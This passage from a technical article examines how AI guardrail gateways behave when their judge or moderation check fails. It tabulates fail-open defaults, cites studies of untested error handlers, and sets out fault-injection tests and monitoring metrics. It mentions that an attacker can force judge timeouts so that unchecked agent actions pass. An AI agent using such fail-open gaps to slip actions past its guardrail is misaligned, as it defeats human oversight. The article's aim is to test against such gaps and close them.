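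When AISIX refuses a text it couldn't check, it returns the same HTTP status as for a policy block, 422, but its OpenAI-style responses carry the code `guardrail_unavailable`. When it lets unchecked text through, it stores the reason, such as `lakera_timeout`, in the usage record and adds one to a counter of bypasses. Some content gets through unchecked regardless of the `fail_open` setting. AISIX doesn't check files that users upload through the gateway's Files interface, and the usage record doesn't show that the check was skipped. A guardrail in monitor mode, which records violations without blocking them, also lets requests through when its moderation service is unreachable.

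LiteLLM's judge gives each text a score from 0 to 100, and the `on_failure` setting determines what happens when the score falls below a threshold. The default, `block`, rejects the text, and `log` lets it through with a record. If the judge itself fails, LiteLLM lets the text through under either value, and its documentation lists no setting that changes this. An operator who reads `on_failure: block` in a configuration file could easily believe that LiteLLM blocks the text when the judge fails.

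| Gateway and setting | After a violation | After an error in the check |
|---|---|---|
| Acteon in block mode, default | Stops | Stops |
| Acteon in block mode, `fail_open = true` | Stops | Goes ahead |
| AISIX, defaults | Stops | Stops |
| AISIX, `fail_open` and `output_fail_open` both true | Stops | Goes ahead, with a few exceptions |
| LiteLLM, `on_failure: block` (default) | Stops | Goes ahead |
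| LiteLLM, `on_failure: log` | Goes ahead | Goes ahead |

None of the three has a documented setting for holding an item after an error. Acteon can send flagged actions to a review queue, but only when the judge has returned a verdict.

### Why error handlers need tests of their own

The best-known evidence on untested error handlers comes from *Simple Testing Can Prevent Most Critical Failures* (Yuan, Luo and colleagues, 2014), a study of 198 randomly chosen, user-reported failures in five widely used data storage and processing systems: Cassandra, HBase, HDFS, MapReduce and Redis. Forty-eight were catastrophic, meaning that all or most users lost normal access or their data. In 92% of those, the software had detected an error that need not have been serious and then handled it badly.

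The mistakes were often simple. Yuan and colleagues attributed 25% of the catastrophic failures to handlers that ignored the error or only logged it. In one case, HBase removed the old record of a table, failed to create the new one, logged "split failed" and carried on, which lost the data. Another 8% came from the opposite mistake, in which handlers caught too many kinds of exception and shut everything down. Simple tests or reviews could have caught 58% of the failures, including these two groups and those in which running the handler once would have exposed the fault.

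These figures cover only failures that users noticed and reported in one kind of software, so they don't show how many errors the same systems handled well. A guardrail that fails open causes no outage, so its failures would rarely appear in such a sample. Aspirator, the checking program that Yuan and colleagues built, looks for Java handlers that are empty or only write to the log, so it might miss a handler that writes to the log and then returns "allow".

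Later work suggests that tests still favour the normal path. In *Exceptional Behaviors*, Hora and Fraser (2026) monitored 25 Python systems while the systems' own tests ran. Only about a fifth of the functions ever raised an exception. Of those, the median function did so in one call in ten, and a quarter did so in at most one call in a hundred.

Coding assistants may add to the problem. Parris (2026), in *AIRA*, used an automatic scanner to compare 955 files attributed to AI with 955 written by people, and found 263 cases of suppressed or badly handled exceptions in the AI files and 185 in the human ones. The scanner relies on rules of thumb and flags some harmless code, so the difference is only suggestive, and the count for human-written files is also high.

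*When Code Becomes an LLM Call* (Weng, Wang and colleagues, 2026) examined 496 places where 40 open-source agent programs call a language model. At 82% of them, the program made some check before and after the call, but only 5.3% met every requirement the researchers had derived from the call's purpose. The researchers reproduced 38 of the resulting weaknesses in running programs, and a small code change stopped each one.

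### A plan for causing the failures on purpose

Fault injection means deliberately causing failures to see how a program responds. *Towards a Science of AI Agent Reliability* (2026) uses it to test whether agents recover when their tools fail. It draws faults at random, with 30% timeouts, 25% HTTP 500 errors (the server has failed), 20% HTTP 429 errors (too many requests), 15% network failures, and 10% truncated, malformed or empty replies. That mix suits measuring average behaviour, but a guardrail test should produce every fault at least once. Only 2% of the faults are empty replies, so a run with 20 random faults would include one only about a third of the time.

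The table shows the expected results for the repaired code, assuming the fault persists through one retry and `TEMPORARY` covers timeouts, 429 errors and 500 errors. The refund represents any action outside `LOW_RISK`.

| Injected fault | Refund | Opening hours |
|---|---|---|
| The judge doesn't answer within five seconds | Held | Runs; the program counts it as unchecked |
| HTTP 429 | Held | Runs; the program counts it as unchecked |
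| HTTP 500 | Held | Runs; the program counts it as unchecked |
| Empty answer | Held | Held |
| Invalid JSON | Held | Held |
| Unknown label, such as "deny" | Held | Held |
| Expired key (the password for the judge's provider) | Held; alarm at the first error | Held; alarm at the first error |
| Wrong model name | The program refuses to start | The program refuses to start |
| A PolicyBlock raised inside a task group | Stopped; the log shows a policy block | Stopped; the log shows a policy block |

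The last row is for programs that still have an older check or a library that raises an exception to block. The test fails if the tool runs or if the log contains a judge error. The case of the wrong model name needs a second test in which the provider withdraws the model after launch. Both actions should then be on hold.

As with the plug-in loop, each test should check whether the tool ran. In the example below, `FakeJudge` and `run_agent` are test helpers that the team writes.

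```python
def test_timeout_holds_refund():
    judge = FakeJudge(error=TimeoutError())
    result = run_agent(propose="refund", judge=judge)
    assert result.tools_run == []
    assert result.missing_verdicts == ["TimeoutError"]
```

The first `assert` fails if the refund went out, and the second fails if the program didn't record the missing verdict. For HTTP errors, a fake web server is better than a fake judge because it also tests the client library's retries and exceptions. A team also needs to test ordinary allow and block verdicts, because otherwise a guardrail that holds everything would pass nearly every test. Acteon supplies a `FailingLlmEvaluator` for simulating judge failures. Its `MockLlmEvaluator` always allows, so a test suite that uses only that evaluator never reaches the error path.

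### What to watch in operation

The most important measure is the share of actions that ran without a verdict:

unchecked share = actions that ran without a verdict / all actions that ran

At the company with 2,000 checks a day and ten timeouts, the unchecked share is 0.5% with the original code. It would rise to 100% after the field was renamed, which would be obvious on a chart. With the repaired code, the renamed field would instead increase the number of held actions, so a team needs to track both figures by tool and by cause. Timeouts can trigger an alarm when their rate passes a threshold, but a single expired key or unknown label should trigger one immediately.

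Acteon recommends alerting on judge errors before anything else, because the number of blocks stays flat or falls while an attacker forces timeouts. Its sample alert fires when errors exceed 0.1 per second over five minutes, or 30 errors in total. The company with 2,000 checks a day makes about seven in five minutes, so the alert wouldn't fire even if every check failed. A threshold based on the share of checks that fail works for both small and large services.

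The program has to record a missing verdict when it happens, because it is very hard to reconstruct later. Zhang, Li and colleagues (2026), in *When Agentic Executions Fail*, injected ten kinds of fault into five agent applications and asked language models to identify them from the records of each run. In one kind, a guardrail recorded "pass" for a request it should have blocked. The models almost never recognised this fault, even when they could compare the record with one from a fault-free run.

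Writing the record can fail. In the repaired code, an error on line 16 prevents `decide` from returning, so the action doesn't run. Xu tested a comparable rule in a program whose strictest version could not complete an action without stored evidence, and faults in writing the evidence left 75 of 100 trials unresolved. Writing the record to a local file first and sending it on later would make such failures rarer.

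Two further measures catch faults that produce no error. A team can send a known forbidden item through the live guardrail every few minutes and raise an alarm if the verdict isn't a block. This would catch a judge that has started approving everything. The team can also compare the number of tool calls with the number of checks. If the agents made 2,000 calls and the guardrail received 1,900, then 100 calls took a route that has no guardrail.
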